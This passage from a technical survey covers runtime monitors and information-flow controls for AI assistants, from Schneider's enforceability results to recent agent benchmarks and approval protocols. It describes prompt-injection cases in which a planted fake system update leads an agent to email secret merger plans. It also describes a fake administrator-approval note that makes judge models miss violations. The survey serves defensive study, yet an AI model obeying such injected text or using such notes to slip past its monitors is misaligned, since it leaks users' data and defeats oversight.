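The second rule in each pair is recursive, meaning it uses the label it defines. A label can therefore pass through any number of steps, whereas the Dogwood policy for typed tools needed a separate rule for each extra copy. Event v3 is untrusted input and v6 depends on it, so v6 is tainted. Event v5 is sensitive input and v6 depends on that too, so v6 is also secret. Since v6 is an outside email, the monitor blocks it, and no model has to recognise the injected instruction.

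This policy blocks an outside email only when it is both tainted and secret. An assistant that reads the medical folder and emails a stranger by mistake, with no untrusted text in its context, would break the user's policy but not this one. To enforce *nothing from my medical folder leaves my accounts*, the last rule has to omit the condition about taint:

```
block(a)     if   a sends something outside, and secret(a)
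```

The graph is also more precise than a single record for the whole session. If one helper reads the medical folder and another confirms lunch, the second helper's message isn't treated as secret unless something from the first helper reached it.

FORGE guarantees that no action the policy denies will take effect, provided that the monitor intercepts every relevant action before it takes effect and the recorded facts correctly describe the events and their dependencies. Recording an unnecessary dependency can only cause extra blocking, but omitting a real one may hide a leak. Someone must also mark the sensitive files, because the assistant can freely forward an unmarked doctor's letter from the downloads folder. FORGE doesn't cover network traffic that bypasses the software libraries it monitors.

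In a small test, a GPT-4.1-mini agent had access to files at four levels of secrecy. A document from an outside company contained a fake system update with instructions to email top-secret merger plans to an "auditor". With only a written instruction not to leak data, the agent sent the plans in all five trials. It did not send them in any of the five trials with the policy above, or in any of the ten with the two military rules at different clearances. In every trial, it also completed a harmless task, emailing a report to a colleague with sufficient clearance.

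The researchers also used FORGE to control what an agent disclosed in OpenClaw. They divided one person's assistant into four agents with separate memories. A manager's agent asked the personal agent whether Alex was free that week, and the first answer mentioned doctor's appointments and stress about a failed client pitch. FORGE used a model to check the answer against a rule that forbade giving reasons, and blocked it. The personal agent then had to rewrite the rejected text without access to the original notes, so it had no new details to add. The second answer gave only the times when Alex was busy or free. This kind of release is useful, but it relies on a model's judgement. The researchers acknowledge that if the model misses a cleverly worded reference to the doctor, the information gets out.

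### Labelling the context or checking the argument

Applying a policy to every information flow makes an agent much less useful because most of its tasks involve reading untrusted data. An experiment on AgentDojo with GPT-4o measured this loss by comparing Fides's two rules with a provenance policy, which checks where each argument of a call came from. Under the provenance policy, untrusted text in the context doesn't block a message if the recipient's address came from the user's request or from trusted records.

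The policy also requires that the user asked for the kind of action the agent is about to take. When the user identifies a target indirectly, as in "delete the largest file", the monitor uses the file listing to find the target and compares it with the agent's choice. At first, the agent could delete the largest file and then the next largest, because a new listing showed the second file as the largest. The researchers added a rule that blocks the deletion if any listing in the context shows a different file as the largest.

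All four arrangements in the table repeated the user's request to the model after each batch of tool results. The figures are averages over five runs of the benchmark.

| Added defence | Tasks completed without an attack | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% |
| A model's list of permitted tools | 73.4% | 69.5% | 3.1% |
| Fides's two rules | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% |
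| Provenance policy | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% |

Fides's rules lowered the agent's task completion by about 50 percentage points when nobody was attacking, while the provenance policy lowered it by 21. Their attack success rates differ by no more than the usual variation between runs. The rates were 0.3% and 0.2%, excluding attacks whose calls the monitor blocked. In every remaining successful attack, the agent recommended the attacker's hotel in its final answer, which FORGE didn't check.

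The provenance policy avoids much of the over-blocking because it is weaker than the medical policy. It requires the destination to come from the user or a trusted record, but doesn't limit what the message contains. If the school's address is in such a record and the user has asked for a reply, the policy allows a reply that mentions peanuts. It would stop an attacker from redirecting the medical folder to a new address, which is the kind of theft AgentDojo tests. The monitor still has to label the folder's contents to keep them from an approved recipient.

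### Fides: keeping secrets out of the model's context

The comparison applied Fides's rules to AgentDojo's standard agent. The full Fides system reduces over-blocking by controlling what the main model reads. When a tool returns data that would tighten the labels on the model's context, Fides stores the data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can use the name in later calls, and Fides fills in the contents and checks their labels just before each call runs.

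For example, Fides could store the allergy file as `file1`. The assistant can still write to a friend about lunch, because its context contains the name `file1` but none of the file's contents. If the assistant tries to call `send_mail(to="office@hillside.example", body=file1)`, the monitor blocks the call because the school isn't allowed to read the contents.

This works well when the assistant can complete the task without knowing what the data contain. Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if a fixed sequence of tool calls and a fixed final response would solve it whatever the tools return. "Complete the tasks due today in my to-do app" is not data-independent, because the assistant has to know what the tasks are.

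For such cases, Fides can ask a second, quarantined model about a variable. This model has no tools and must answer in a fixed format. In the museum example, the main model could ask for the fee as a number and receive 18. The policy can then endorse a number from that source without exposing the main model to the rest of the message. Willison proposed this arrangement, the dual LLM pattern, in 2023. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) explains that, in terms of labels, its advantage is that untrusted data never taint the planning model's context.

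In their AgentDojo tests with GPT-4o, Costa and colleagues found that Fides completed 8% more tasks on average than a basic agent under the same kind of enforcement. With OpenAI's o1, an early reasoning model, the gain was 16%. With the policy checks off, Fides completed 6.3% fewer tasks than the basic agent because of the extra steps for hiding and revealing data. Fides stopped every injection attack in the benchmark when it had suitable policies, but hiding the data without them let some attacks through.

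The formal guarantee is explicit secrecy, which concerns data that a program copies or computes from a secret. It doesn't cover what an observer can infer from the assistant's choice of actions. If the assistant orders a peanut-free lunch for Mia, the caterer learns something about the contents of the medical folder even if no text from it appears in the order.

Microsoft (2026) has since added Fides to its Agent Framework as an experimental feature. It labels each piece of content as trusted or untrusted and as public or private, and checks the labels before a sensitive tool runs.

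### Tracking capabilities in a programming language

Fides attaches labels while the agent runs. A compiler can do some of this work in advance if the agent writes a program instead of making calls one at a time. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, which runs agents' programs in a restricted form of Scala 3. A program can reach files or the network only through capabilities, which are ordinary values in the code. Scala's type system records which capabilities each piece of code can use.

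TACIT puts secret data in a wrapper called `Classified`. The program can process what is inside by passing a function to the wrapper's `map` method, but the function must be pure, meaning that it uses no capabilities at all. In the example below, `allergies` is a wrapped text and `mail` is a capability to send messages:

```
allergies.map(text => text.toUpperCase)          // accepted
allergies.map(text => mail.send(school, text))   // rejected
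```

The first function only changes the text, and its result stays in a new wrapper. The second uses `mail`, so the compiler rejects the program before it runs. As in the reply to Boebert, code that can read the secret has no channel for sending it, but here the principle applies within one program. The rest of the program can still use `mail`.

In the main example, an agent compares classified contracts and summarises the changes. Its program retrieves the wrapped documents, finds the differences, passes them to a second model for a summary and writes the result to a file. The agent's own model writes this program without seeing the contracts, so it wouldn't learn what they contain even if an attacker fully controlled it. Opening the wrapper requires a separate capability, which the user may have but the agent doesn't.

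The compiler also has to prevent less direct escapes. A program could try to keep a file capability past its permitted lifetime by hiding it inside a function. The function's type would include the capability, so the compiler would reject the attempt. Errors are harder to control. A program could be written to divide by zero only if the file's text contains "peanut", so a crash would reveal that the word is there. TACIT catches errors while the program runs and turns them into values, which it can put back in the wrapper.

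Types can't stop the second model from keeping what it reads or using it to answer later questions, so TACIT relies on whoever runs that model to prevent this. Users must also trust the compiler and the library that provides the capabilities. Odersky and colleagues report that agents could write programs in this form with no significant loss in task performance. But each agent needs a set of typed tools, and data-dependent tasks remain difficult because the agent's model can't look inside a wrapper to decide what to do next.

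### PACE: what path tracking adds and what it blocks

Li, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *PACE*, measured how much tracking contributes when a monitor also checks what the user authorised. PACE has three parts that the researchers could switch on and off:

- Path confinement blocks a call if a recorded path leads from secret or untrusted data to an unsafe effect.
- Effect verification checks the effects of the call against permissions derived from the user's request. It covers matters such as the operation, confidentiality and budget.
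- Boundary adaptation can restore a call that path confinement blocked if effect verification approves it, or repair a call in a way declared in advance.

They ran all eight combinations on the same 1,167 cases with Qwen-3.8-27B. The table gives attack success, then completion of the user's tasks, for five of the combinations on three of the benchmarks.

| Parts switched on | AgentDojo | AgentDyn | PASB |
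|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% / 76.8% | 25.0% / 66.7% | 41.4% / 100% |
| Path confinement | 0% / 13.6% | 0% / 0% | 31.0% / 0% |
| Effect verification | 0% / 64.6% | 1.7% / 36.7% | 0% / 100% |
| Both of these | 0% / 65.2% | 1.7% / 36.7% | 0% / 100% |
| All three | 0% / 67.2% | 0% / 33.3% | 0% / 100% |

Path confinement stopped the attacks on AgentDojo and AgentDyn mainly by preventing the agent from acting at all. On PASB, it blocked every legitimate task, yet nearly a third of the attacks still succeeded. In the complete system's AgentDyn runs, PACE identified a path to cut in 5,842 of 6,647 recorded calls (88%). It never succeeded in rewriting a call on this benchmark to remove only the dangerous part. Tasks succeeded because effect verification restored calls that path confinement had blocked.

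Effect verification accounts for most of the security gain, and Li and colleagues acknowledge that the full combination showed no unique security benefit. Path tracking can still help enforce the medical policy. The benchmarks mostly test whether an attacker can make the agent do something the user didn't request, and comparing the agent's actions with the request can catch that without tracking data. But the user did request a reply to the school, so the monitor has to track what information went into it.

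On the full benchmarks, the complete system lost at most three percentage points of task completion compared with an agent without a defence. On the AgentDyn cases in the table, it lost 33 points, so the loss depends heavily on the tasks. The version that Li and colleagues tested also lacks the strongest guarantee. Their proof that an action can't complete a recorded path from a secret to an unsafe effect applies only if PACE keeps the cut in place, and restoring a blocked call can reopen the path.

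The evaluation also included other defences. On AgentDojo, a conventional tracker that labels data at every step reduced task completion from 62.6% to 29.8% with Qwen and from 73.8% to 56.0% with GPT-5.6-luna. With GPT-5.6-luna, the most effective group of attacks still succeeded 55% of the time. On WASP, a benchmark of web tasks, agents completed between 0% and 60% of the tasks with Fides, depending on the model, and between 79% and 87% without a defence. Attacks on WASP also succeeded more often with Fides than without it, so the version tested may have been poorly suited to the benchmark.

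PACE tries to be more selective by comparing the arguments of each call with data it has recorded. It also searches for registered secrets in plain text and in a fixed set of encodings. Li and colleagues acknowledge that this search misses paraphrases, translations and secrets split into pieces. Their guarantee also excludes text the model has put into its own words, which includes most of the mail an assistant writes. If the allergy file contains the word "peanuts" and the assistant asks the school to keep Mia away from satay, the search finds no match. A label on everything the model wrote after reading the file would catch that request but also block the message about lunch.

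## Which policies blocking can enforce and which it cannot

A better search than PACE's might catch the request about satay, but no monitor can enforce the sixth example policy, *answer the school within a day*. A monitor can only block calls, and an assistant that makes no calls breaks this policy. Researchers have worked out in general which policies a monitor cannot enforce.

### Runs and safety properties

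A run is the sequence of events as an assistant works, including the messages that arrive and the tool calls that take effect. It may go on indefinitely, since an assistant has no natural end. A policy P can be treated as the set of runs it permits, with all other runs forbidden. For example, *never delete mail* is the set of all runs in which no mail is deleted.

A policy is a safety property if every violation becomes visible at some finite point and nothing that happens later can repair it:

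```
x ∉ P   ⇒   x has a finite beginning u such that every run starting with u is ∉ P
```

The first three example policies are safety properties, a technical term that doesn't mean the permitted runs are harmless. A run permanently violates one of them at the moment the assistant deletes a message, writes to a stranger or makes the payment that takes the month's total past $200. *Ask me before anything that cannot be undone* is also a safety property, because a run violates it when an irreversible action takes effect without earlier approval.

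If the user had told the assistant to answer the school but set no deadline, the assistant could still comply by replying after a month of silence. This policy isn't a safety property, because no finite initial stretch of the assistant's behavior can permanently violate it.

### Monitors that can only stop a program

Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) shows that monitors that watch a program's steps and halt it before it breaks a policy can enforce only safety properties. The monitor observes a single run, so whether a run complies must depend on that run alone. The monitor also has no access to future steps. If it allows a forbidden beginning because a later step might repair it, the program may stop before that step. The monitor therefore has to halt the program at some finite point, and only when no later steps could make the run comply.

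The monitors in earlier sections block one call and let the assistant try another, but Schneider notes that this option doesn't add to the policies a monitor can enforce. Monitors with memory, such as HCAP's state machines and Sapien's patterns, stay within the class because they decide from the run so far. Several monitors working side by side can enforce all of their policies at once, so a user could have a separate monitor for each limit.

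One of Schneider's examples is close to the school's deadline. After a customer pays for a service, the policy forbids the seller to do anything except provide it. A monitor can enforce this, but the seller can still keep the money and do nothing. The stronger policy, that payment guarantees service, is not a safety property. Likewise, if a monitor blocked every call except a reply to the school, the assistant could still send no reply.

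Some policies can't be judged from one run at all. Suppose two assistants both read the medical folder before ordering Mia's lunch:

| The folder lists | First assistant orders | Second assistant orders |
|---|---|---|
| a peanut allergy | a peanut-free lunch | a peanut-free lunch |
| no allergies | a standard lunch | a peanut-free lunch |

Suppose one assistant orders a particular lunch only if Mia has an allergy, while another always orders it. If Mia has the allergy, both assistants place the same order, but a caterer who knows their habits can infer the allergy only from the first assistant's order. Whether the order reveals the allergy depends on what the assistant would have ordered if Mia didn't have it, and a monitor never sees that run.

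Schneider concludes that this kind of monitor can't enforce a ban on information flow exactly, but it can enforce a stricter policy that is a safety property. FORGE similarly blocks every outside action that its graph links to a secret. That rule would block both assistants' orders, including the one that reveals nothing.

### Holding actions back and inserting new ones

*Edit Automata* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2003) studies more powerful monitors, which can suppress an action, insert one of their own, or do both. A monitor that can do both can hold an action back and release it later. Such a monitor must be sound, meaning that everything it outputs obeys the policy, and transparent, meaning that it doesn't change the meaning of a run that already obeyed the policy.

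In the paper's main example, a customer at a market must pay for any apples they take but may pay before or after taking them. A monitor that can only stop the program has no good response when a customer takes apples first. If it lets the action through, the customer may never pay, and if it stops the program, it may interrupt an honest purchase. A monitor that can also hold actions back and release them later withholds the apples until the customer pays, then lets both actions through together.

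Ligatti and colleagues prove that this technique can enforce any policy if a program can decide whether each finite run obeys it. The monitor holds back every action until the sequence so far obeys the policy. However, the proof assumes that doing nothing obeys every policy. This is true of the market but not of the school's deadline, so the theorem doesn't apply to obligations like the sixth policy.

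Holding actions back also requires a program that can continue for a while without their results. If the monitor must deal with each action before it sees the next, and the program may attempt actions in any order, the monitor can again enforce only safety properties, despite its extra powers. Assistants mostly work this way, because the model needs the result of one call to choose the next. A monitor can usually delay an outgoing email for an hour, but it can't delay a train booking while the model is waiting for the booking reference.

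Inserting actions has limits too. In another example, a passenger boards a San Francisco cable car without showing a ticket, and the monitor inserts the missing action. This is harmless because showing a ticket twice has the same effect as showing it once. Similarly, a monitor could insert a standard message to the school saying that the family will reply soon. It couldn't insert the actual answer, because it can't determine whether Mia is going on the trip, and a wrong answer might be worse than none.

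### Why blocking cannot meet a deadline

The deadline formally turns the sixth policy into a safety property, because once a day has passed without a reply, no later message can undo the violation. Yet a monitor still can't enforce it. Schneider noted this exception and explained that stopping a program doesn't stop time from passing.

Basin, Jugé and colleagues, in *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, a 2012 paper, turned his observation into a general condition. They separate the actions a monitor can control from the events it can only observe, such as the ticks of a clock, and compare two policies:

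- After a failure, nobody may log in for three time units.
- After a request, the system must deliver within three time units.

Both policies are safety properties in the usual sense, but the monitor can enforce only the first by blocking actions. A login that comes too soon breaks the first policy, so the monitor can block logins until enough time has passed. The second policy is broken when the deadline passes without a delivery. Until that moment the run still obeys the policy, because the system could deliver in time, and when the deadline passes there is no action for the monitor to block.

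Basin and colleagues therefore require not only ordinary safety but also that every violation become irreparable at an action the monitor can control. The school's deadline fails this test because the violation becomes irreparable when the day ends, which the monitor cannot control.

Replacing time with a count of steps makes the policy enforceable but useless. A monitor could enforce "answer the school within 20 tool calls" by halting the assistant after the 20th call, which would leave the school without an answer.

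The policy *Ask me before anything that cannot be undone* also requires an action, but only before another one. The monitor can block the irreversible action until the user has approved it. If the assistant never asks, nothing irreversible happens and the policy holds. In general, a monitor that controls Y can enforce "do X before Y", but blocking can't make the assistant do X.

Restricted capabilities can't enforce obligations either, because meeting an obligation requires something to act. Taking away a permission removes some of an assistant's options, but never the option of doing nothing. It can even cause a missed deadline. If the monitor blocks a reply that mentions peanuts and the assistant gives up, the medical policy holds but the school gets no answer. A monitor with a clock could alert the user after 20 hours, but the user would then have to write the reply.

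### What changes for assistants

The classical results concern programs whose actions a monitor can recognise with certainty. Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, lists four ways in which assistants depart from this picture:

- A policy may depend on a judgment that can be wrong, such as whether an email contains personal information.
- Many actions have irreversible effects outside the system.
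- Actions carry unbounded data, such as any recipient and any amount, so no finite list of actions can cover them.
- Text from strangers can influence what the assistant tries to do.

Ray handles these in separate theorems, each with its own assumptions, and doesn't claim that any one result covers all four. The paper therefore uses "certified" in two senses. One is that a monitor keeps to a policy on every possible sequence of proposed calls, provided it receives correct answers to questions such as "does this contain personal information?". The other is that the average probability of a violation stays below a chosen limit, under stated statistical assumptions. Neither implies that the assistant is safe in general.

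Suppose a monitor must allow, block or replace each call before it takes effect. Every run it produces must obey the policy, and it must leave runs that already obey the policy unchanged. Ray proves that such a monitor can enforce a policy if and only if the policy is a safety property and a machine with the monitor's kind of memory can recognise which finite beginnings of a run are still acceptable.

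One direction of the proof constructs a monitor that tracks the run so far and blocks any call that would make the run unacceptable. This works because blocking has no outside effect in the model, so it can't break a safety property.

The other direction, that blocking can enforce only safety properties, follows by contradiction. Suppose a monitor enforces a policy that isn't a safety property. Then some forbidden run could, after any number of calls, still continue as a permitted one. The monitor must not disturb permitted runs, so it has to allow each next call. It therefore allows the whole forbidden run, which contradicts the assumption that it enforces the policy.

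This monitor differs from the one at the apple market because it deals with irreversible effects. Ray's example is a policy that every payment must eventually be followed by a confirmation. A monitor could enforce this by holding each payment until the confirmation arrived, but a museum sends confirmation only after it has the money. The monitor can't retract a payment if no confirmation comes, and if it blocks the payment, it prevents a purchase that would have complied with the policy.

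Ray's running example is an assistant for email and payments. Two of its policies meet both conditions. One is a daily cap on transfers to each recipient, and the other is a ban on sending anything after the user revokes access. The daily cap needs a trusted clock to record the day of each transfer. The monthly $200 limit also meets the conditions if the clock records the month. Ray also places Progent's rules in this class.

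### Checking whether a policy makes sense

A user might also want a program to check, before a policy is used, whether it can ever block anything, since a mistake could leave a rule that never applies. Ray proves that no program can check this for every policy if the rule language has two counters that can go up and down and be tested for zero. Such counters are enough to simulate any computer program, so one could write a policy that blocks a call only if a given program eventually halts. No general method can determine whether a program halts.

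A checker can answer the question if the rules are written in a more restricted language. In this language, counters can only go up, each is compared only with fixed numbers, and the counters for one recipient don't affect those for another. Once a counter passes the largest number in the rules, its exact value no longer matters, so the checker has only finitely many cases to examine. Because all recipients have the same rule, it needs to check only one recipient.

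Daily caps fit this language without a reset, because each new day gets a new counter. ToolFence's reservations don't fit, because the number of held uses goes down when a payment fails. A monitor can still enforce limits with reservations, but Ray's method for checking a policy in advance doesn't cover them.

### When the judge can be wrong

*Send nothing that would embarrass me* is a safety property, because a single embarrassing message violates it permanently. But such messages are hard to recognise. If a language model scores how embarrassing each draft is, and the monitor blocks drafts that score above a threshold, the monitor will sometimes miss an embarrassing message and sometimes block a harmless one. Lowering the threshold reduces the misses but blocks more harmless messages.

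With any given information about a draft, a monitor has a lowest possible rate of false blocks at each miss rate. Ray takes this limit from a theorem in statistics, the Neyman–Pearson lemma. Better prompts, or several models that vote, can bring a monitor closer to the limit but can't do better than it without more information. For example, the same joke may be fine for a friend and embarrassing in front of a manager, so a monitor that sees only the text can't get both cases right.

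Small miss rates add up. If the judge misses 2% of embarrassing drafts and its mistakes are independent, the chance that at least one of 20 gets through is 33%:

```
1 − (1 − 0.02)^20  ≈  0.33
```

Ray's statistical certificate comes from conformal risk control. Someone collects n examples of violations, and the judge scores them. To keep the miss rate at or below m, the monitor ranks the scores from lowest to highest and uses the one in position (n + 1) × m, with the position rounded down, as its threshold. If that position is zero, the monitor has to block everything. To avoid this, the user would need at least 19 examples of embarrassing messages for a 5% miss rate, and at least 99 for 1%. The examples must also be representative of those the assistant will write in future, which few users could ensure.

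Ray tried this with 23 judges on 132 short texts from AgentDojo (97 user requests and 35 attacker goals). Given one of each, the judges scored the attacker's goal higher 66% to 86% of the time. Holding back half the attacker goals for testing left too few examples for a 5% limit, so every judge had to block everything. At a 10% limit, Gemma-2-9B missed 1% of the attacker goals but blocked 78% of the harmless requests.

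The texts contained only instructions, without the conversation or tool results that a real monitor could use. On a separate set of 60 tool calls, a judge model with seven billion parameters, which is small by current standards, met the 10% limit while blocking only 3% of the harmless calls. The share of harmless calls that must be blocked to get a certificate therefore depends heavily on the task and the judge.

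Context can also matter more than the action itself, but a record of where an instruction came from helps a judge only if the judge uses it. In another test, Ray took 123 tool calls from AgentDojo and showed each to a judge twice, with the same instruction coming once from the user and once from a tool's output. The call was authorised only when the instruction came from the user. The 7B judge gave the unauthorised version the higher score in 116 cases. A 3B judge did so in 15 and gave equal scores in the other 108.

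The certificate doesn't cover an attacker who changes what the judge reads. Ray added a 16-token note claiming that an administrator had already approved the action. At a fixed threshold, this raised the miss rate of eight of 11 judges by 20 to 60 percentage points. The monitor can allow for such attacks by using a stricter threshold, but only if someone has established the most that any attack of that size could raise the miss rate. Trying some attacks shows only that this maximum is at least as large as the biggest increase they caused.

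### Blocking changes what the assistant does next

A judge's error rates also don't determine how well a monitor will work. Ray describes two systems that behave identically when nobody blocks them. After a block, one stops and the other tries a new violation. Recordings made without a monitor look the same for both systems, so they can't be used to predict which one will need a second block.

To measure the effect directly, Ray ran a 7B agent on 949 AgentDojo cases with and without a judge:

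| Judge | Share of calls blocked | Attack success | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 4.7% | 25.4% |
| 7B model | 12% | 3.2% | 24.3% |
| 3B model | 78% | 0.4% | 18.0% |

The 3B judge stopped most attacks by blocking most calls. The 7B judge's effect on attacks was small enough to be due to chance. In a separate comparison on 389 matched cases, 34 attacks succeeded only without the 3B judge, and five succeeded only with it. For the 7B judge, the figures were 29 and 22. Ray attributes the attacks that succeeded only with a judge to the way blocking changes the agent's later actions.

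### Harm from actions that are each allowed

Suppose the assistant is planning a weekend away, and the user says, "Don't leave me with a train ticket and no hotel." The assistant buys a non-refundable ticket, intending to book the last room in town, but someone else takes the room first. Buying the ticket didn't break the policy, because the assistant could still have booked the room. The harm came from the sale of the room to someone else, which the monitor could observe but not block.

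The user can prevent this with a stricter policy that lets the assistant buy a non-refundable ticket only after booking a hotel that offers free cancellation. A monitor can enforce this policy because it can block the ticket purchase. But the policy also blocks purchases that would have turned out well, and the assistant can't buy a non-refundable ticket to a town where no hotel offers free cancellation.

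Other combinations are harmful in ways that nobody thought to forbid. The assistant could book the train for one weekend and the hotel for another, for a total of $190. Both payments comply with the spending limit, and a monitor with memory could compare the dates only if someone had written a rule about them. Muruaga's lists of forbidden pairs likewise miss any harmful pair that nobody thought to list.

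Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) reviewed 38 studies in *Toward Safe LLM Agents* and found that the guarantees of runtime monitors cover only single steps or short sequences. In one study of customer-service tasks, monitors blocked 94% of unsafe actions, but in most settings agents completed fewer than 5% of the tasks both safely and correctly because they found other unsafe routes. The reviewers rate the certainty of this evidence as very low because it comes from a single study. The airline experiments with gates had much better results, so the outcome may depend on the tasks and on how completely the rules cover them.

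### How many requirements plain checks can enforce

The theory divides policies into types but doesn't show how common each type is. TACL's 90% figure covered only enforceable cases. *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (Hong, She and colleagues, April 2026) also counted unenforceable ones.

A review of 80 benchmarks for the security and safety of agents found that 49 gave the agent no explicit requirements, and 19 gave only broad goals, such as refusing anything "unsafe", without defining the word. Only five had rules that applied to all of an agent's tasks and were precise enough to check. All five were for agents with a narrow job and a fixed set of tools. None of the 55 benchmarks for general-purpose agents had such rules.

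The researchers then analysed three sets of requirements. Two came from benchmarks with precise rules: τ²-bench, for its airline agent, and CAR-bench, which tests a voice assistant in a car. The third was for MedAgentBench, whose agent works with medical records. It had no such rules, so the researchers had language models generate them, partly through an automated analysis of possible hazards. For each requirement, they decided whether ordinary code could enforce it.

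| Agent | Enforceable requirements | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Airline | 42 of 51 | 82% |
| Car | 17 of 18 | 94% |
| Medical records | 34 of 57 | 60% |
| All three | 93 of 126 | 74% |

Simple methods were enough for 88 of the 93 enforceable requirements. Most needed only a check before a tool runs, for example that the ticket being cancelled belongs to the customer. Others needed a fixed format for the model's output, a confirmation request that ordinary code sends to the user, or a prewritten message. The remaining five, all for medical records, needed rules about the order of actions or the flow of information.

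Hong and colleagues found four recurring themes among the requirements that code couldn't enforce. Some requirements were about tone, such as staying neutral. Some prohibited made-up information, and some set a procedure, such as asking for a customer's details before the details of the trip. The rest took common sense to apply. For instance, the airline agent may offer compensation only if the customer explicitly asks for it, but customers can ask in many ways.

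Rewording such a rule can make it enforceable, but also changes it. One suggested version blocks compensation until the customer's reply exactly matches the word "compensation". A monitor can check that with certainty, but a customer who writes "I want my money back" would get no compensation.

In another experiment, the agents had all the rules in their instructions, with no code to enforce them. They broke at least one enforceable rule in 20% to 78% of tasks, depending on the model, the benchmark and whether the user tried to manipulate them. The checks prevented these violations by design. Task completion didn't fall with the checks in any comparison, and for the car assistant it rose from 59% to 72%.

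These figures are weak evidence about personal assistants. The 74% comes from three agents with narrow jobs, and language models wrote the requirements for one of them. The researchers classified the requirements by hand, and they left ten of the enforceable medical requirements out of the experiment because writing the checks would have required medical expertise. The share also weights all requirements equally, whether they concern message format or payments. A personal assistant has many more tools, and its user is unlikely to write rules as carefully as an airline does. The share for such users could be much lower, and nobody appears to have measured it.

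### The seven policies compared

The table assumes that the assistant can't bypass the mechanism and that the descriptions of its tools are correct. A stateless token has fixed limits, which the service checks without any record of earlier uses.

| Policy | Per-call rules | Stateless tokens | Monitor with memory | Flow tracking | Model as judge |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Never delete mail | yes | yes, if the service can exclude deletion | yes | not needed | not needed |
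| 2. Write only to contacts | yes, with a current list | yes, if tokens can name recipients | yes | not needed | not needed |
| 3. At most $200 this month | no | no, because each use passes separately | yes, if it covers every session and agent | no | no, without a reliable total |
| 4. Nothing leaves from the medical folder | only by closing the folder or blocking all outside contact | only by withholding one of the two permissions | roughly, by blocking outside contact once the folder is open | yes for recorded flows, with many false blocks | catches some disclosures |
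| 5. Ask before anything irreversible | yes, if each call can wait for an answer | yes, if the token requires the user's confirmation | yes, and it can reuse an earlier approval | can show whether an approval came from the user | can guess which actions are irreversible |
| 6. Answer the school within a day | no | no | no, but it can warn the user | no | no, but it can assess a draft reply |
| 7. Send nothing embarrassing | no | no | no | no | partly, with misses and false blocks |

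## Replanning and asking the user after a refusal

When a monitor refuses a call, the task is still unfinished. Suppose it blocks the assistant's reply to the school's invitation because the reply mentions a peanut allergy. The assistant could find another plan that its permissions allow, such as saving the reply as a draft for the user to send. It could do only part of the task, by accepting the invitation without mentioning the allergy. It could also ask the user for permission to send that one sentence, or stop and report the problem.

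Doing less isn't always the cautious choice. The school asked about allergies, so a reply that leaves them out may suggest that Mia has none. If the assistant drops part of a task, it has to tell the user, and here it should also tell the school that the answer is incomplete.

### Choosing a plan within the grant

Zhou and Zhang argue that least privilege should begin when the assistant chooses a plan, before anyone works out which permissions the plan needs. They state the condition this way:

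```
choose π ∈ Π_q(g)   such that   A(π) ⊆ G
```

Here g is the user's goal, and Π_q(g) is the set of plans that achieve it with at least quality q. A(π) is the set of permissions plan π requires, and G is the set the user has granted.

In an example adapted from theirs, the user asks how much the family spent on prescriptions last year. The receipts are in the medical folder. The assistant may read the folder and run programs on the user's machine, but nothing from the folder may leave the user's accounts.

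| Plan | Permissions it requires | Within the grant? |
|---|---|---|
| Upload the receipts to an online service that adds them up | read the folder, send its contents to the service | no |
| Add them up with a program on the user's machine | read the folder, run a local program | yes |

If the monitor blocks the upload, the assistant can switch to the local program without asking the user for anything. A tool like MiniScope wouldn't find this alternative, because it only finds the smallest set of permissions for the plan it is given. The upload plan does need both permissions, so the user would get a permission request that looked unavoidable.

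The local program might fail to read some receipts. If the total isn't accurate enough, no plan meets the condition. The assistant can then offer a partial total, ask whether an estimate would do, or request permission to upload only the unreadable receipts. Sometimes neither of two plans is clearly less intrusive, for instance when one reads more private files and the other discloses a little information to an outside company. Zhou and Zhang suggest showing the user both options in such cases.

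An assistant often has to explore before it knows what a plan requires, so Zhou and Zhang propose authorising limited exploration first, such as listing the files in a folder, and treating any further access as a separate request. The assistant's estimate of A(π) can be wrong, but the monitor still checks every call, so an underestimate leads to another refusal rather than a breach. This works only if the limits stay the same when the plan changes. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), an interview and survey study of software practitioners, also recommends keeping the limits fixed.

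When *AC4A* denies access, its dashboard shows the user which permission is missing, so that the call can succeed when retried. This is convenient, but it steers the user towards granting more permissions. Zhou and Zhang propose that the permission request also mention any less intrusive alternative.

### What an approval should cover

The fifth example policy, *ask me before anything that cannot be undone*, requires the monitor to hold a call until the user answers. The user needs to see everything that could change their answer, such as the amount, the payee, the recipients and the full text of a message. The assistant's model shouldn't write the description the user sees, because a model misled by an injected instruction might describe a museum ticket when the call pays someone else.

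Yu, Geng and colleagues (2026), in *SUDP*, describe a protocol that ties each approval to an exact operation. A separate program called the custodian holds the user's passwords and keys, and the assistant never receives them. A purchase would work like this:

1. The assistant proposes an operation in a fixed format, such as one payment of $42 to City Museum before 6 PM.
2. The custodian adds a random value that works only once and sends both to the user's device.
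3. The device displays the operation. If the user agrees, the device signs a fingerprint of the operation and the random value.
4. The custodian computes the fingerprint again from the operation it received. If the signature matches, it makes the payment and returns only the result to the assistant.

The fingerprint is:

```
β = H( label ‖ r ‖ H(o) )
```

H is a hash function, which turns any text into a short value. Finding two texts with the same value is infeasible. The operation is o, the random value is r, and the label marks what the fingerprint is for. If the assistant changes $42 to $420 after the user agrees, H(o) changes, the signature no longer matches β, and the custodian refuses. An approval can't be reused, because the custodian has already used up r. The custodian stores the credentials encrypted, and the approval carries the key that unlocks them, so a thief who copies the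 stored data can't use it.

Yu and colleagues prove six of their seven security properties under standard cryptographic assumptions. The seventh, protecting secrets in the custodian's memory while it is working, requires special hardware. The proofs also assume that the user's device displays the whole operation and that the approved operation fully determines what happens, neither of which cryptography can guarantee. If the user approves only "email the school", for example, the assistant could choose the text afterward.

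Products have failed in both ways this design tries to prevent. *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) examined 17 security advisories for three agent products. In 12, the approval didn't cover what the agent did, and in the other five, the approval remained in force after the facts it was based on had changed.

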